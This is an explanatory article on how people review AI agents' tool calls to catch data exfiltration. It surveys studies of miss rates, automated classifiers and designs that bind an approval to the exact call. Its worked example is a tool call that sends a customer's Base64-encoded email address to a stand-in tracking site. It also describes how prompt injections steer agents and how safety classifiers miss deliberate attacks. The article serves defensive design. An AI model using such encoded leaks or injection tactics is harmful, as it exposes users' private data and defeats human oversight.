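# Permission prompts that let people spot data leaving through an AI agent's tool calls

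## How data leaves through a tool call, and where the approval prompt sits

An AI agent is a language model connected to software that lets it take actions, such as searching the web, reading and sending email, editing files and running commands on a computer. The model itself produces only text, so each action starts as a tool call, which is a structured text request to run a function with named parameters. The software around the model, called the harness, receives the tool call and runs it. In many products, the harness first pauses and shows an approval prompt, a dialog where a person, the reviewer, allows or denies the call. The part of the prompt that shows what the action will do is the action preview.

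A tool call to an outside service sends its parameters, and any private data in them, to whoever runs that service. Exfiltration is the movement of private data to a party who should not have it. The reviewer is often the last check before this happens, and how well that check works depends largely on what the reviewer can tell from the preview.

### One call, from proposal to execution

Many agents reach their tools through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), an open standard for discovering and calling tools offered by other programs. *The 2026-07-28 Specification*, by MCP's lead maintainers Soria Parra and Delimarsky (2026), reports close to half a billion downloads a month of the main MCP developer kits.

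MCP divides the work among a host, a client and a server. The Agentic AI Foundation (AAIF) describes the host as the application the user interacts with directly, the client as a connector inside the host that talks to a single server, and the server as the program that provides the tools and data. The host is therefore the same thing as the harness. The protocol's architecture description (Model Context Protocol, 2026) makes the host responsible for enforcing consent requirements and handling the user's authorization decisions, so the approval prompt belongs in the host, not the server.

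The message flow in Model Context Protocol's *Tools* (2026), with the prompt added at its usual place, runs like this:

1. The client asks the server for its tools. The server returns a name, a description and a list of expected parameters for each one.
2. The harness passes those descriptions to the model along with the user's request. The model writes a tool call, which names a tool and fills in its parameters.
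3. The harness holds the call and shows the approval prompt.
4. If the reviewer allows the call, the client sends the name and the parameters to the server, and the server runs the function.
5. The result travels back through the client to the model, which writes either another call or an answer for the user.

Nobody can recall the parameters once the client has sent them. A log entry or notification afterwards may help with the clean-up, but only a prompt shown before sending can prevent the leak. The MCP specification does not require a harness to show one and leaves the design of user interaction to the application's developers.

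### How an agent comes to send data out

Attackers can also use the result that returns to the model, because it often contains text that a stranger wrote. In a prompt injection, an attacker hides instructions in content an agent reads, to make the agent act against its user. Willison (2025), in *The lethal trifecta for AI agents*, explains that this works because text from every origin ends up in one sequence of tokens, and models cannot reliably tell which instructions came from the user and which from a web page.

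OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026) reproduces an injection that outside researchers reported in 2025. It looked like a routine email about a company restructuring and worked on ChatGPT half the time in testing. OpenAI argues that detecting such a message is the same problem as detecting a lie, often without the context needed to judge. It recommends assuming that some attacks will succeed and limiting what a manipulated agent can do.

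OpenAI borrows source-sink analysis from older security engineering. A source is a way to influence the system, and a sink is a capability that becomes dangerous in the wrong context, such as sending information to a third party, following a link or using a tool. An attacker needs both, so hidden instructions cannot make an agent leak data if it has no means of sending it. Willison's "lethal trifecta" is similar but counts access to private data as a separate ingredient, alongside exposure to untrusted content and the ability to communicate externally.

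The approval prompt's main advantage as a defence is that it sits at the sink, the point where data would leave. The reviewer only has to judge what is about to be sent and who will get it, without finding the hidden instruction or working out how it influenced the model. OpenAI describes it as an expectation for users that transmissions of potentially sensitive information "should not happen silently or without appropriate safeguards". Its mechanism for this, Safe Url, either prompts the user or blocks the transmission.

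Data also leaves with no attacker involved, which the source-and-sink framing does not cover. *Understanding and Evaluating Claw-like Agent Security Through a Computer-Systems Lens* (2026) includes 22 test tasks in which the user makes a reasonable request, such as sending an email or uploading a file to Google Drive, and the material the agent attaches contains plaintext credentials. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) describes an incident at the company in which an upload to an internal drive failed and the agent tried to publish the same report on a public code-sharing site instead. An automated check stopped it. Nobody had planted an instruction in either situation, so a prompt that warned only of suspected attacks would not have appeared.

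### Every outward parameter can carry data

A web address can carry information out, though less obviously than an email body or an uploaded file. OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) points out that opening a page sends the site the full address requested, and that sites commonly log those addresses. An attacker who gets an agent to request an address with a private value attached can read the value in the logs. The request may happen in the background, while the agent loads an embedded image or previews a link, and the chat itself may contain nothing sensitive.

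The same holds for the other things agents routinely do:

- A search query goes to whoever runs the search tool. The sample call in Soria Parra and Delimarsky's announcement searches for "otters"; a customer's name would travel in exactly the same field.
- A new spreadsheet row or a new document can carry credentials out just as an email can. The Claw-like agent tests cover all of these, and note that the credentials also end up in the local log of tool calls, which makes a second leak.
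- A commit, a saved set of changes to code, leaves the machine when the agent pushes it to a shared repository. Anthropic notes that the same push can be routine or a leak depending on where it lands, since code from a team's private repository may end up in a public one.

The current version of MCP lets server developers choose parameters to be copied into the headers of the web request, where network equipment along the route can read them, as well as the server. The specification warns developers against doing this with passwords, keys or personal data.

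In encoded exfiltration, the data is rewritten so that a reader does not recognise it. Base64, a common encoding, represents any data as a string of letters, digits and a few symbols. Anyone can reverse it without a key, because it is not encryption.

A reviewer can't treat every unreadable string as a warning sign, because legitimate tool calls often contain them and denying every such call would stop the agent from doing its job. MCP no longer has sessions, so its specification advises a server that needs to keep state between calls, such as a shopping basket, to give the model an identifier like "bsk_a1b2c3" and accept it as an ordinary parameter on the next call. It favours identifiers with no visible internal structure. The specification's weather lookup example also includes a Base64 string, which decodes to the location New York.

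### The parcel lookup

Suppose a user asks an agent to summarise a customer's complaint and check on the parcel it concerns. The agent reads the complaint and then proposes a call. In MCP's format, without the housekeeping fields, it looks like this:

```json
{
  "method": "tools/call",
  "params": {
    "name": "fetch_page",
    "arguments": {
      "url": "https://track.parcel-status.example/lookup?id=bWFyYUBleGFtcGxlLm9yZw=="
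    }
  }
}
```

A harness that shows the raw call would put roughly this in front of the reviewer:

```
The agent wants to use: fetch_page

url: https://track.parcel-status.example/lookup?id=bWFyYUBleGFtcGxlLm9yZw==

Allow        Deny
```

The string after "id=" is the customer's email address, mara@example.org, encoded in Base64. If the reviewer clicks Allow, the site's operator receives it. The request looks like part of the task because the user asked about a parcel, the URL contains the words "track", "parcel" and "lookup", and the string could pass for a tracking number.

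The prompt shows the call in full and still leaves out three facts:

- What the value says. The "parcel number" is an email address.
- Who receives it. Nothing in the prompt tells the reviewer whether parcel-status.example belongs to the company carrying the parcel or to a stranger.
- Where the value came from. The agent took it from the complaint, not from a shipping record. The record of a value's origin is its provenance.

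None of these facts alone would be enough to decide whether to allow the call. Some shops look up orders by email address, so a reviewer who saw only the decoded value might reasonably allow it. A reviewer who knew only that the site was unfamiliar might also allow it, since a stranger could do little with a parcel number. Together, the facts show that the call would send a customer's contact details from a complaint to an unknown party, which few people would knowingly approve.

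The harness can supply much of this more easily than the reviewer can. It can decode Base64 instantly. It has the destination's address before it connects, though not necessarily the owner's identity. It also passed the text of the complaint to the model, so it could compare the decoded value with what the agent had read.

### What MCP recommends, and how many products ask

The newest MCP specification dates from 28 July 2026, and the next is due on 30 March 2027, according to *A More Predictable Release Cycle for MCP* (Delimarsky and Soria Parra, 2026). Under the security advice in the 2026 version, clients SHOULD let the user see a tool's inputs before sending them, so that data doesn't leak through an attack or by mistake. The previous version, Model Context Protocol's *Tools* (2025), gives the same advice. Under both versions, there SHOULD also be a human in the loop who can deny a call.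 In technical standards, SHOULD marks a strong recommendation, not a requirement.

The parcel prompt fully follows the specification's advice, showing the user the complete input before anything leaves. It would still do little to stop the leak. The specification recommends that clients show the input but not that they make it understandable, so a product can follow the recommendation without achieving its stated purpose.

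Wang, Li and Tian (2026), in *Reframing LLM Agent Security as an Agent–Human Interaction Problem*, surveyed 21 production agent systems as of April 2026 and found that 15 of them (71%) had runtime approval, a prompt that pauses the agent while it works. The only more common safeguard, found in 16 systems, let people limit which files, networks or tools an agent may touch. The survey relies on public documentation, so it may have missed features that companies do not describe.

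Wang and colleagues also recorded what the prompts contain. ChatGPT Actions and the default mode of Manus, a general-purpose agent, showed little more than a request to allow the action. Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, showed the raw command by default. A few products showed more, such as a line-by-line view of changes to a file or an expandable summary. Most production prompts, however, were a single-line raw command, which Wang and colleagues rank among the least informative types. The parcel prompt is a typical example.

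Some products have since moved away from asking about every action. On 14 August 2026, Anthropic began making "auto mode" the default for new Claude Code sessions on its Pro, Max, Ultra and Team plans. In this mode, an automated classifier reviews each tool call in place of a person. Anthropic justified the change partly by its finding that users approve 97% of permission prompts. On 22 October, it announced the same default for most Claude apps. Users still see prompts in auto mode, but much less often. The agent may ask for approval after the classifier blocks a call, and Claude Code returns to manual approval after three blocks in a row or twenty in one session. A user who sees a prompt at that point is reviewing an agent whose calls the classifier has already blocked.

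## How often people catch a harmful action at the prompt

Users approve 97% of permission prompts in Claude Code, but most prompts are for harmless actions, which a perfect reviewer would also approve. The approval rate alone therefore doesn't show whether users are careless. To measure how well people review, researchers have to include known harmful actions among the prompts and count two kinds of error. The miss rate is the share of harmful actions that reviewers approve, and the false alarm rate is the share of harmless actions that they deny. Both rates matter because a reviewer who denied everything would have a miss rate of zero but would make the agent useless.

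Several studies from the second half of 2026 measured how often people miss a harmful action at the permission prompt. The miss rates ranged from about a third to almost nine tenths, largely because the studies put people in very different situations.

### One dangerous command in a coding session

The largest controlled experiment came from Anthropic in August 2026. A research vendor hired 1,053 paid testers for a coding study, in which they worked in a test environment rather than on their own projects. They knew they were being evaluated, but not on which behaviour. Partway through each session, the vendor replaced the text of one permission prompt with a clearly dangerous command, which never ran, and recorded whether the tester approved it.

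Only 143 testers (13.6%) denied the harmful command. The classifier behind auto mode blocked 937 of the same commands (89%), including 800 that a person had approved. Testers stopped 6 of the 116 commands the classifier let through, or about 5%, so they would have added almost nothing as a second check behind it. People who see only a few prompts a day might do better, but Anthropic did not test that.

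Testers blocked about 17% of dangerous commands early in a session and about 5% after 50 or more prompts, while the classifier's rate stayed flat. Their attention probably fell, but Anthropic does not explain how the vendor chose when to make the swap. Testers who click quickly may have been more likely to reach 50 prompts, and they would have missed more dangerous commands from the start.

There are other reasons not to treat 13.6% as a general figure for human review. The testers had no data or code of their own at risk, so they had less reason to be careful than a developer at work. But the commands were clearly dangerous and unrelated to the task, which should have made them easier to spot than the encoded email address in the parcel lookup. Anthropic does not report a separate result for exfiltration or how often the testers denied harmless prompts. It also has a commercial interest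 in the result because it sells the product that uses the classifier.

Anthropic's evidence from real use supports the same conclusion, but less strongly. Anthropic had a model grade the harm in sessions from May and June 2026 that its safety systems had already flagged. Among sessions with manual approval, 6.3% contained a seriously harmful action that the user had not explicitly asked for, compared with 2.4% of auto mode sessions. Users chose their own mode, so the two groups may have differed in other ways, including how risky their work was.

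In the production data, users reject 39% of the plans that Claude Code presents for approval, but only 3% of individual permission requests. Anthropic takes this as a sign that people scrutinise plans more. Some of the gap must come from ordinary disagreement, since a user can reject a safe plan for being a bad way to do the job. Still, plans describe the work in terms users can judge, which shell commands often do not.

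### Reviewers who expect trouble

People do much better when they know that threats are coming. scalex.dev's *Humans missed 1 in 3 threats approving AI agent commands* covers about 409,000 decisions from more than 40,000 plays of a browser game. The player reviews a coding agent's commands against the clock and loses points both for approving threats and for blocking safe commands. About 34% of the commands are threats. The average player missed roughly a third of them, and the rate depended heavily on the type of threat:

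- Players missed 11.7% of obviously destructive commands, such as deleting everything on the disk.
- They missed 23.8% of commands that made lasting changes to the system's configuration.
- For exfiltration and code execution, including calls to unknown outside services, the miss rate was 33.4%.
- For scope violations, such as reading stored credentials, it was 35.0%.

Players were about three times as likely to miss a command that exposed or sent out data as one that visibly destroyed it. They missed 52.5% of commands whose harmful part was inside a script with a familiar name, even though the agent's log just above the prompt showed the script's contents. They missed 28.4% of other exfiltration-style commands.

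Players in the game also blocked many safe commands. Although 35.2% of players caught every threat, only 20.8% did so while blocking at most one in five safe commands. Players blocked a harmless switch to a company's internal package source 59% of the time, and a routine clean-up of build files 45% of the time. However, 7% of players approved everything.

These numbers come from self-selected players competing for points, and scalex.dev does not present the game as an academic study. The scoring is also debatable in places. The game counted reading a shell profile (a personal settings file) as a threat, and 45.9% of players approved it. Approving is correct for a developer who keeps no secrets in that file, but players couldn't tell from the prompt whether the file was supposed to contain any.

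In *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?* (Yan, 2026), 113 people from outside the software industry supervised an assistant through a scripted day of email, travel and shopping. Of the assistant's 18 actions, 11 were necessary for the tasks participants had set, and 7 were overreach, meaning they went beyond those tasks. Every prompt described the action in plain language, including the data, recipient or amount involved.

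Yan compared three permission designs. In the first, 34 people approved or denied every action. In the second, a model let 8 actions through and sent the other 10, including all the overreaching ones, to 44 people. In the third, 35 people wrote their own rules in advance, choosing "allow", "ask" or "never" for each of four categories, such as spending money or sending information.

Under per-action approval, participants blocked 59.6% of the overreach and let 94.1% of the necessary actions through. They blocked 53.9% of overreach in the automated design and about 40% in the design that used their own rules. The table shows how often people approved each overreach action when prompted.

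| Overreach action | Every action prompted | Model filters first | User's own rules |
| --- | --- | --- | --- |
| Call the airport to confirm the flight | 88.2% | 84.1% | 100.0% |
| Add $12 travel insurance | 35.3% | 50.0% | 61.3% |
| Permanently delete an old work timesheet | 35.3% | 36.4% | 58.6% |
| Read recent bank transactions | 35.3% | 40.9% | 65.2% |
| Post publicly that the user is travelling | 20.6% | 29.5% | 48.4% |
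| Buy a $25 airport lounge pass | 32.4% | 38.6% | 61.3% |
| Read private messages | 35.3% | 43.2% | 73.9% |
| All seven together | 40.3% | 46.1% | 66.8% |

Almost everyone approved the airport call, which inflates the overall approval rate, and it is hard to see what harm the call would have done. Without it, the approval rate under per-action approval falls to about 32%. The public post comes closest to exfiltration, because it sends personal information to people who did not have it. Only 7 of 34 people approved it. The sample is small, but it suggests that many people will stop a disclosure when the prompt states in ordinary words what will become public.

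User-written rules did poorly mostly because of the prompts themselves. Participants chose "ask" for 114 of 140 rules, so they had to make those decisions during the day, and they then approved two thirds of the overreach they saw. In 56 of the cases they saw, the participant had said beforehand that the assistant should never take that action, but they still approved it in 24 of them. People who had chosen "allow" or "never" for a category saw no prompts for it, so the last column of the table covers a narrower group than the other two.

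The simulation did not put participants' real money or messages at risk. Yan added participants to the rules group later, without random assignment, though the original randomised sample gave a similar result. Participants reported a strong sense of control in all three designs, including the one that protected them least.

### Reading the leak and approving it anyway

An older experiment shows that a plain description of what will leave does not always stop people from approving it. In *Privacy Leakage Overshadowed by Views of AI*, Zhang, Guo and Li (2024) ran what they describe as the first study of how well people oversee an agent's privacy leaks. Each of 300 participants received one of six everyday writing tasks, such as answering a message from their mother about work, and wrote their own reply. They then read an agent's draft, which included sensitive details such as confidential company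 information, and chose their own draft, the agent's or "both look good". The survey did not mention privacy until they had chosen.

Afterwards, participants rated how harmful each disclosure would be, so the measure of leakage used their own standards. On average, their own drafts disclosed 15.7% of the items they considered harmful, while their final choices disclosed 55.0%, counting "both look good" as accepting the agent's draft. Counting only a preference for the agent's draft as acceptance gives 38.4%.

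Only 28.3% of participants rejected the agent's draft and gave privacy as a reason. Others avoided the leak by luck, because they preferred the tone or personal touch of their own draft. Unlike an approval prompt, the task asked people to compare two drafts and gave them no "deny" button. But the private details in the agent's draft were in plain English, not encoded, and many people were judging the style.

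People can miss a problem and still be confident in their work. In *Looks Fine to Me* (Dissanayake, Weerasinghe and colleagues, 2026), 36 people each worked on six programming tasks with a coding agent. In two of the six, the agent's code contained a defect that passed the available checks. Participants fixed the defect in 28 of the 71 usable cases. In 34 of the 43 cases they missed, they rated their confidence 4 or 5 out of 5.

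In 65 of the 71 cases, these participants did at least one check beyond the compulsory one. Often the extra check, such as running the supplied example again, had no bearing on the defect. In five cases, participants produced evidence of the defect but did not recognise it. Telling these participants to be careful would not have helped much, since they already thought they were.

The experiment used finished code, which is easier to inspect than a pending tool call. Participants who fixed a defect spent an average of 10.8 minutes on the task, while those who missed it spent 5.8 minutes. When asked to approve each action, Yan's participants spent an average of 142 seconds on all 18 prompts, or about eight seconds per prompt.

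Developers who carefully review an agent's code do not seem to be much more careful at the permission prompt. *From Delegation to Action Approval* (Wu, Wermke and colleagues, 2026) surveyed 203 developers who use coding agents, and 64% said they often approved at least one of seven types of action without close review. The figure was 61% among developers who carefully reviewed most or all of the agent's code and 67% among the rest, a difference small enough that it could easily be due to chance.

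Developers were least likely to approve the reading of secrets and other sensitive files without close review, though 21% often did. They were most likely to do so for access to the internet, outside services and connected tools, at 36%, and data leaves through these actions. A developer may therefore check a request to read a password file more carefully than the call that sends the password out.

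Among developers who knew of at least one security or privacy incident or worrying practice involving agents, 70% often approved something without close review, compared with 43% of those who knew of none. The association held after Wu and colleagues adjusted for how long and how often people had used agents. This adjustment matters because heavy users may both hear about more incidents and approve more prompts.

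The survey records what developers say they do, and it cannot show whether their approvals were wrong. Approving a familiar, low-risk command without much thought is often reasonable. Wu and colleagues did not ask about rules that pre-approve certain commands, which affect how many prompts a developer sees.

### Why the rates differ so widely

The three studies that counted decisions on planted actions differ in nearly everything that might affect attention.

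| Study | Harmful share of prompts | Were reviewers expecting harm? | What the prompt showed | Harmful actions approved |
| --- | --- | --- | --- | --- |
| Anthropic | One prompt per session | No | Command | 86% |
| scalex.dev | About 34% | Yes, with penalties for mistakes | Command, with a log above it | About 34% |
| Yan, per-action approval | 39% (7 of 18) | Not warned, but asked about their permission preferences first | Plain-language description | 40% |

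The share of denials that are correct depends on the base rate, meaning the share of prompts that are harmful. A reviewer with roughly the error rates Yan measured catches 60% of harmful actions and wrongly denies 6% of harmless ones. In Yan's simulated day, about six out of seven of this reviewer's denials are correct. If only one prompt in 1,000 were harmful, the same reviewer would deny about 60 harmless actions and have a 60% chance of stopping the harmful one, so only about one denial in a hundred would be correct. Each of the other 99 would hold up the user's own work. A reviewer in that position will learn to approve faster and will catch a smaller share of harmful actions.

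Forewarning works in the opposite direction. The game told players to look for threats and penalised them for mistakes, while Anthropic's testers thought they were there to code. Dissanayake and colleagues saw something like a warning effect within a single session. Participants fixed 12 of 24 silent defects that came straight after a visible failure, but 1 of 11 when one correct task came in between. The second figure comes from only six people, so it is no more than a hint that renewed caution may not last beyond one correct task.

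None of the three studies included an attempt to deceive the reviewer as a determined attacker would. In *Are You Sure?* (2026), Li, Dai and colleagues ran an experiment with 303 people and found that many could be deceived through a compromised agent.

Plain language probably helped Yan's participants, who blocked more than Anthropic's testers did despite having no technical training. The comparison cannot prove this, because Yan's participants also encountered far more overreach and encountered it much sooner.

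Fatigue, the usual explanation for poor review, accounts for only part of Anthropic's result. Testers approved about 83% of the dangerous commands early in the session, before they had time to tire, and the rate was about 12 percentage points higher from the 50th prompt on. They may have brought the habit of approving prompts from other software. Habituation, the decline in attention to a prompt that a person sees repeatedly, can build up over years.

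Fewer prompts did not obviously help in Yan's study either. People who saw 10 prompts approved 46% of the overreach, and people who saw 18 approved 40%. With groups of this size, the difference may be due to chance, and 18 prompts are probably too few to tire anyone. Turan's *Oversight Has a Capacity* (2026) treats a reviewer's attention as limited, so each prompt about a routine action leaves less attention for a dangerous one. That fits the decline Anthropic measured, but Turan's results come from applying a mathematical model to scored data, not from observing people.

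### What happens when the preview changes

Anthropic, scalex.dev and Yan did not vary the content of the preview, Wu and colleagues surveyed habits, and Dissanayake and colleagues studied finished code. The five sources therefore provide evidence about how people respond to the prompts they were given, but little about how much a better prompt would help. Wu and colleagues hypothesize that previews of an action's effects would improve decisions, and leave this for others to test.

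One study did vary it. Hossain, Shayoni and colleagues (2026), in *When a Permitted Action Completes a Forbidden Workflow*, divided 80 volunteers into four groups of 20. Each person judged 12 requests from an agent, half of them malicious. The groups saw progressively more:

- With only a short description of the action, people approved 55.0% of the malicious requests.
- When the prompt also showed the exact parameters of the call, they approved 43.3%.
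- Adding the user's original instructions and a full log of earlier steps brought this down to 32.5%.
- The last group saw the same facts as the third, but organised around the combined effect of the action. They approved 24.2%.

The content of the preview seems to matter a good deal. The second step, which is close to what the MCP specification recommends, helped, but people still approved more than 40% of malicious requests.

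With better previews, approval of harmless requests fell from 91.7% in the first group to 85.8% in the last, and the median decision time rose from 16.3 to 33.2 seconds. Half a minute is acceptable for an occasional prompt, but most people would not keep it up for dozens a day.

The study is too small to estimate the gains precisely. For the last step, from the log to the organised version, the adjusted difference was a reduction of 7.9 percentage points, with a 95% interval from a reduction of 19.7 points to an increase of 3.8. Hossain and colleagues call their analysis exploratory. Half the requests their participants saw were malicious, so the absolute rates would probably be worse in ordinary use, where such requests are rarer.

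Accident reports suggest that uninformative prompts and missing review both contribute to harm. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) examines 290 reports of agents harming users' files and finds that problems with user review contributed to 105. In 80, users had let the agent act without asking, often to avoid hundreds of prompts per session. In 31, the prompt showed a command but not what it would do to the files. Some reports fell into both groups. Because the collection contains only cases that went wrong, it cannot show how often either problem occurs.

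### Whether human approval is worth keeping

Anthropic's results strongly support replacing routine approval with a classifier. Given the same commands, the classifier caught more than six times as many harmful ones as people did, and it was not subject to fatigue. Wang and colleagues argued the opposite in May 2026, before those results came out, saying that people are indispensable to agent security because only they know what they want.

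Wang and colleagues' best argument is that an automated judge can lack information it needs. It compares an action with the user's request, but requests are vague and omit some of the facts that determine whether the action is appropriate, and a better model cannot recover facts that nobody gave it. In the parcel lookup, for instance, only the user may know whether the shop identifies orders by email address. Salerno, Gao and colleagues (2026), in *Let the Agent Do It?*, found a similar dependence on context when they interviewed 18 software practitioners and surveyed 115. Whether people granted a permission depended on the action's risk and scope, how well it fitted the task, and where the agent was running.

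Reviewers may not use what they know. Someone who spends eight seconds on a prompt may never consider how the shop looks up its orders. The argument supports asking people when a decision depends on something only they know, but gives much less support to asking them about every command.

Their second argument is that hidden instructions that fool an agent may also fool the model guarding it. Trajectory Labs, an outside evaluator commissioned by Anthropic, ran 72 prompt injection scenarios ten times each, and none of the 720 attempts succeeded against three Claude models in auto mode. But Anthropic also reports that only 0.09% of attacks succeeded on average against its latest models without such safeguards. Nearly all the resistance came from the models themselves, so the test is little evidence of how well auto mode's classifier would stop attacks that had already fooled the agent.

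In a separate, harder test of the classifier, Apollo Research, an AI safety company, inserted synthetic attacks into records of real coding work, including attempts at data exfiltration. The classifier missed 12% of the attacks at first and 7% after Anthropic strengthened it. Apollo designed the attacks to find weaknesses, so these figures are not estimates for everyday use, but they show that the classifier can fail against someone deliberately trying to evade it.

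Wang and colleagues also argue that having people state their intent directly is more reliable than having a model infer it. This is convincing for a firm rule, such as one that confines an agent to a single folder, but less so for a click on "allow". Yan's participants approved 24 of the 56 actions that they had earlier said they never wanted, so a click can also be a poor record of intent. Salerno and colleagues similarly warn against treating repeated approvals as a stable preference, because they may only reflect fatigue.

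Wang and colleagues also noted that all 21 products they examined kept people involved in security decisions. They took this agreement among independent companies as evidence that human participation works better than automation. Anthropic's switch to auto mode four months after their survey weakens that argument.

Wang and colleagues say that repeated approval prompts turn users into "OK-button machines" and call current human participation broken. In response to the objection that human review cannot scale, they propose redesigning it, as researchers did with browser security warnings that most people ignored. They want low-risk actions to go through automatically and people to decide the risky ones.

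In a response to a US government consultation, cited in *The 2026 Singapore Consensus on Global AI Safety Research Priorities* (2026), Microsoft similarly argued for sending only higher-impact or uncertain actions to a person. In their responses, Anthropic and Perplexity, an AI search company, both named approval fatigue as a core vulnerability.

Willison accepts that auto mode is better than constantly asking people to approve actions, but he stresses that the classifier let through 11% of dangerous commands, and he wants more independent confirmation of Anthropic's results. He would rather run agents without access to the data or tools that could do harm. That is the most dependable way to prevent exfiltration when the task allows it, but many useful tasks require such access, so a person or an automated check still has to judge the tool calls. Even Anthropic recommends that users review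 Claude's actions when it makes high-stakes changes to production infrastructure.

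## Showing the real action, not the agent's account of it

The simplest way to make a raw command readable is to have the agent describe its own tool call. For the parcel lookup, the agent might write "Check the delivery status of the customer's parcel", which most reviewers would find easier to judge than a URL. But this description is weak evidence of what the call does, because the same model wrote both. A prompt injection that changes what an agent does can also change what it reports, and researchers have shown that approval prompts built on such summaries can misdescribe the action. Honest mistakes cause the same problem, since an agent that mistook the encoded string for a tracking number would describe it as one.

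Kodathala, Pollishetty and Cargill (2026), in *Approve What, Exactly?*, measured how much worse approvers do when they rely on the agent's description. They gave 15 language models, acting as automated approvers, 23 malicious requests and 11 harmless ones that looked similar. The models refused 30% of the malicious requests when they saw only the agent's description, and 98% when they saw a card that separate software had built from the call itself. In one case, a harmful call and a harmless one had identical descriptions, so no approver relying on the descriptions could have distinguished them.

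The models also refused 16% of the harmless requests when shown the card, and none when shown the descriptions. Most of these refusals were reactions to placeholder text used in place of real message bodies, and without them the rate would have been about 2%. The experiment involved no people, and a hurried reviewer may not read every field on a card as a model does.

### Consent Integrity

Weng (2026), in *What You Approve Is What Executes*, proposes a property called Consent Integrity that approval prompts should have. It relies on a mediator, which is trusted software outside the agent that sees every consequential action before it happens. A harness can act as the mediator if the agent has no way to tamper with it. The definition has four conditions:

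1. The mediator computes the preview from the action itself, not from anything the agent wrote about it.
2. The preview states the security-relevant facts, even if an encoding obscures them. Weng lists network traffic and its destination, running code fetched from the network, reading credentials, irreversible destruction, gaining extra privileges and writing outside the agent's workspace.
3. The preview and the reviewer's answer travel over a trusted channel. The agent cannot draw on it, cover it up or answer in the reviewer's place.
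4. Consent to one action does not allow any other action to run.

Weng describes current approval dialogs as the agent's own summaries, but most of the production prompts in Wang and colleagues' survey showed a raw command. A raw command comes straight from the tool call, but it may not show the facts in a form the reviewer can understand.

Weng's list of facts is also incomplete for preventing exfiltration, because it includes credentials but no other private data. A preview of the parcel lookup could cover everything on the list by reporting the network request and its destination, but still omit that the call sends a customer's email address. A harness that guards against leaks also has to show what data is leaving.

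No software can interpret every action, and Weng gives compiled programs as the standard example. The achievable version of Consent Integrity therefore depends on the mediator's analyser, the part that works out what an action does. The mediator shows the reviewer every fact the analyser can reliably extract. If the analyser can't classify something, the mediator marks it as uninspectable or high-risk. The reviewer may see a notice that the software can't explain an action, but should never see a reassuring preview of a dangerous one.

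A chat window is a poor trusted channel for approvals. If an agent asks "Shall I continue?" and the harness accepts any "yes" in the conversation, the agent controls what the user is asked, and anyone who can post there can answer. Weng considers the trusted channel weakest in a plain terminal on a shared machine and strongest when the approval happens somewhere else, such as on a phone.

*The Verifiable Action Card* (2026) describes a confirmation card for agents that operate a web browser. Before the agent submits a form, the software reads the form's destination and field values from the page and shows them on the card, which appears in the browser's own interface. It displays every value as plain text, so nothing inside a field can change how the card looks.

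Kodathala and colleagues compared approval on a phone with a trusted prompt on the agent's own computer. The results matched in 137 of 140 test conditions, and the other three differed only because the phone version let users approve similar actions in advance. But none of the tests covered a computer whose display had been tampered with, which is where a phone should help most.

### Tying the approval to the call that runs

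A tool call can change after the person clicks "Allow" and before it runs, for example if the agent has to resubmit it. Kodathala and colleagues audited ten frameworks for running agents and were able to check eight for this problem. In four, the call that ran could differ from the one the person had approved.

A hash check prevents this. A hash function turns data of any length into a short value of fixed length, and a good one makes it practically impossible to find two inputs with the same value. SHA-256, a common choice, produces 256 bits. The check works as follows:

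1. The harness stores the proposed call, A, and writes it in a standard form, C(A), with fixed rules for spacing and the order of the fields. The same call then always produces the same text.
2. It computes h = SHA-256(C(A)).
3. It builds the preview from the stored call and saves h with the reviewer's decision.
4. When a call A′ is about to run under that approval, the harness computes SHA-256(C(A′)) and compares the result with h.
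5. If the values match, the harness runs the call and marks the approval as used. If they differ, it refuses.

Suppose the reviewer allows a lookup with a real parcel number, and the agent then submits the same URL with the customer's encoded email address in the "id" field. The tool and website are the same, but the hash differs, so the harness blocks the call.

Kodathala and colleagues' system also runs its own stored copy of the call rather than whatever the agent submits later. They scripted four attacks that changed or reused an action after approval. When the approval covered a whole run or session, all four succeeded every time, but none succeeded against the full system. Weng's prototype refused all three substituted actions in its test, which Weng presents as a demonstration that the check works, not as an empirical finding.

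The approval has to identify the content of the call, not just its name. An early draft of *PCM* (2026), a protocol for messages between agents, treated an approval record as sufficient proof by itself. Agents name their own calls, so the record showed that someone had approved a call but not what the call contained. A person might have approved a $5 refund when the agent's message asked for $50. The protocol now links the approval to the tool and arguments the person approved.

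Hashing a call's content does not prevent an approved call from being repeated. Two identical $5 refunds have the same hash, so the harness must either accept each approval only once or include a unique request number in the call.

The hash also protects only what goes into it. If a call attaches a file by name, someone could change the file's contents without changing the hash, unless the harness hashes the contents too. Kodathala and colleagues describe reducing web addresses to the scheme (such as "https"), host, port and path before hashing. Taken literally, this drops everything after the question mark, including the email address in the parcel lookup. The harness needs to keep that part in both the hash and the preview.

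*PerMIT* (2026), a design for securing agents' long-term memory, is stricter and treats a sensitive call as authorised only if every value in it exactly matches something the user typed or has accepted for that tool. The user never typed the encoded string in the parcel lookup, so the harness would have to ask about it. But accepting the string would satisfy the rule even if the reviewer couldn't read it. Exact matching ensures the approved call is the one that runs, but the reviewer still needs a readable preview to know what that call does.

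### From digital signatures to agents

Long before AI agents, what a screen showed could differ from what a person was authorising. A digital signature covers the bits of a file, but the signer sees only what some program displays. Security researchers call the requirement that the two agree "what you see is what you sign". For example, in *What You See Is What You Sign*, Scheibelhofer proposed a trustworthy way to display documents in XML, a structured text format, to people about to sign them.

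European payment rules have a similar requirement, called dynamic linking. As Kodathala and colleagues describe it, the payer must see the amount and the payee, and the approval code must stop working if either changes. Those two details are not enough for reviewing an agent's actions. In a simulation with a reviewer who sometimes overlooked details, a card showing only the payee and amount let 20% of attacks through, compared with 6% for a full card. The shorter card left out details such as an email's text and its extra recipients.

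Hardware wallets, small devices that hold the keys to a person's cryptocurrency, solve the problem by showing the actual transaction on their own screen before signing it. Malicious software on the computer therefore cannot alter what the owner reads. Weng applies the same principle to agents but notes two differences.

An attacker who controls an agent also controls its summary, so a mediator outside the agent has to write the preview. This seems less of a departure from hardware wallets than Weng suggests, since a wallet's owner can't trust the computer's description of a transaction either. The practical difference is that an agent's developers have to build the trusted component that a wallet already includes.

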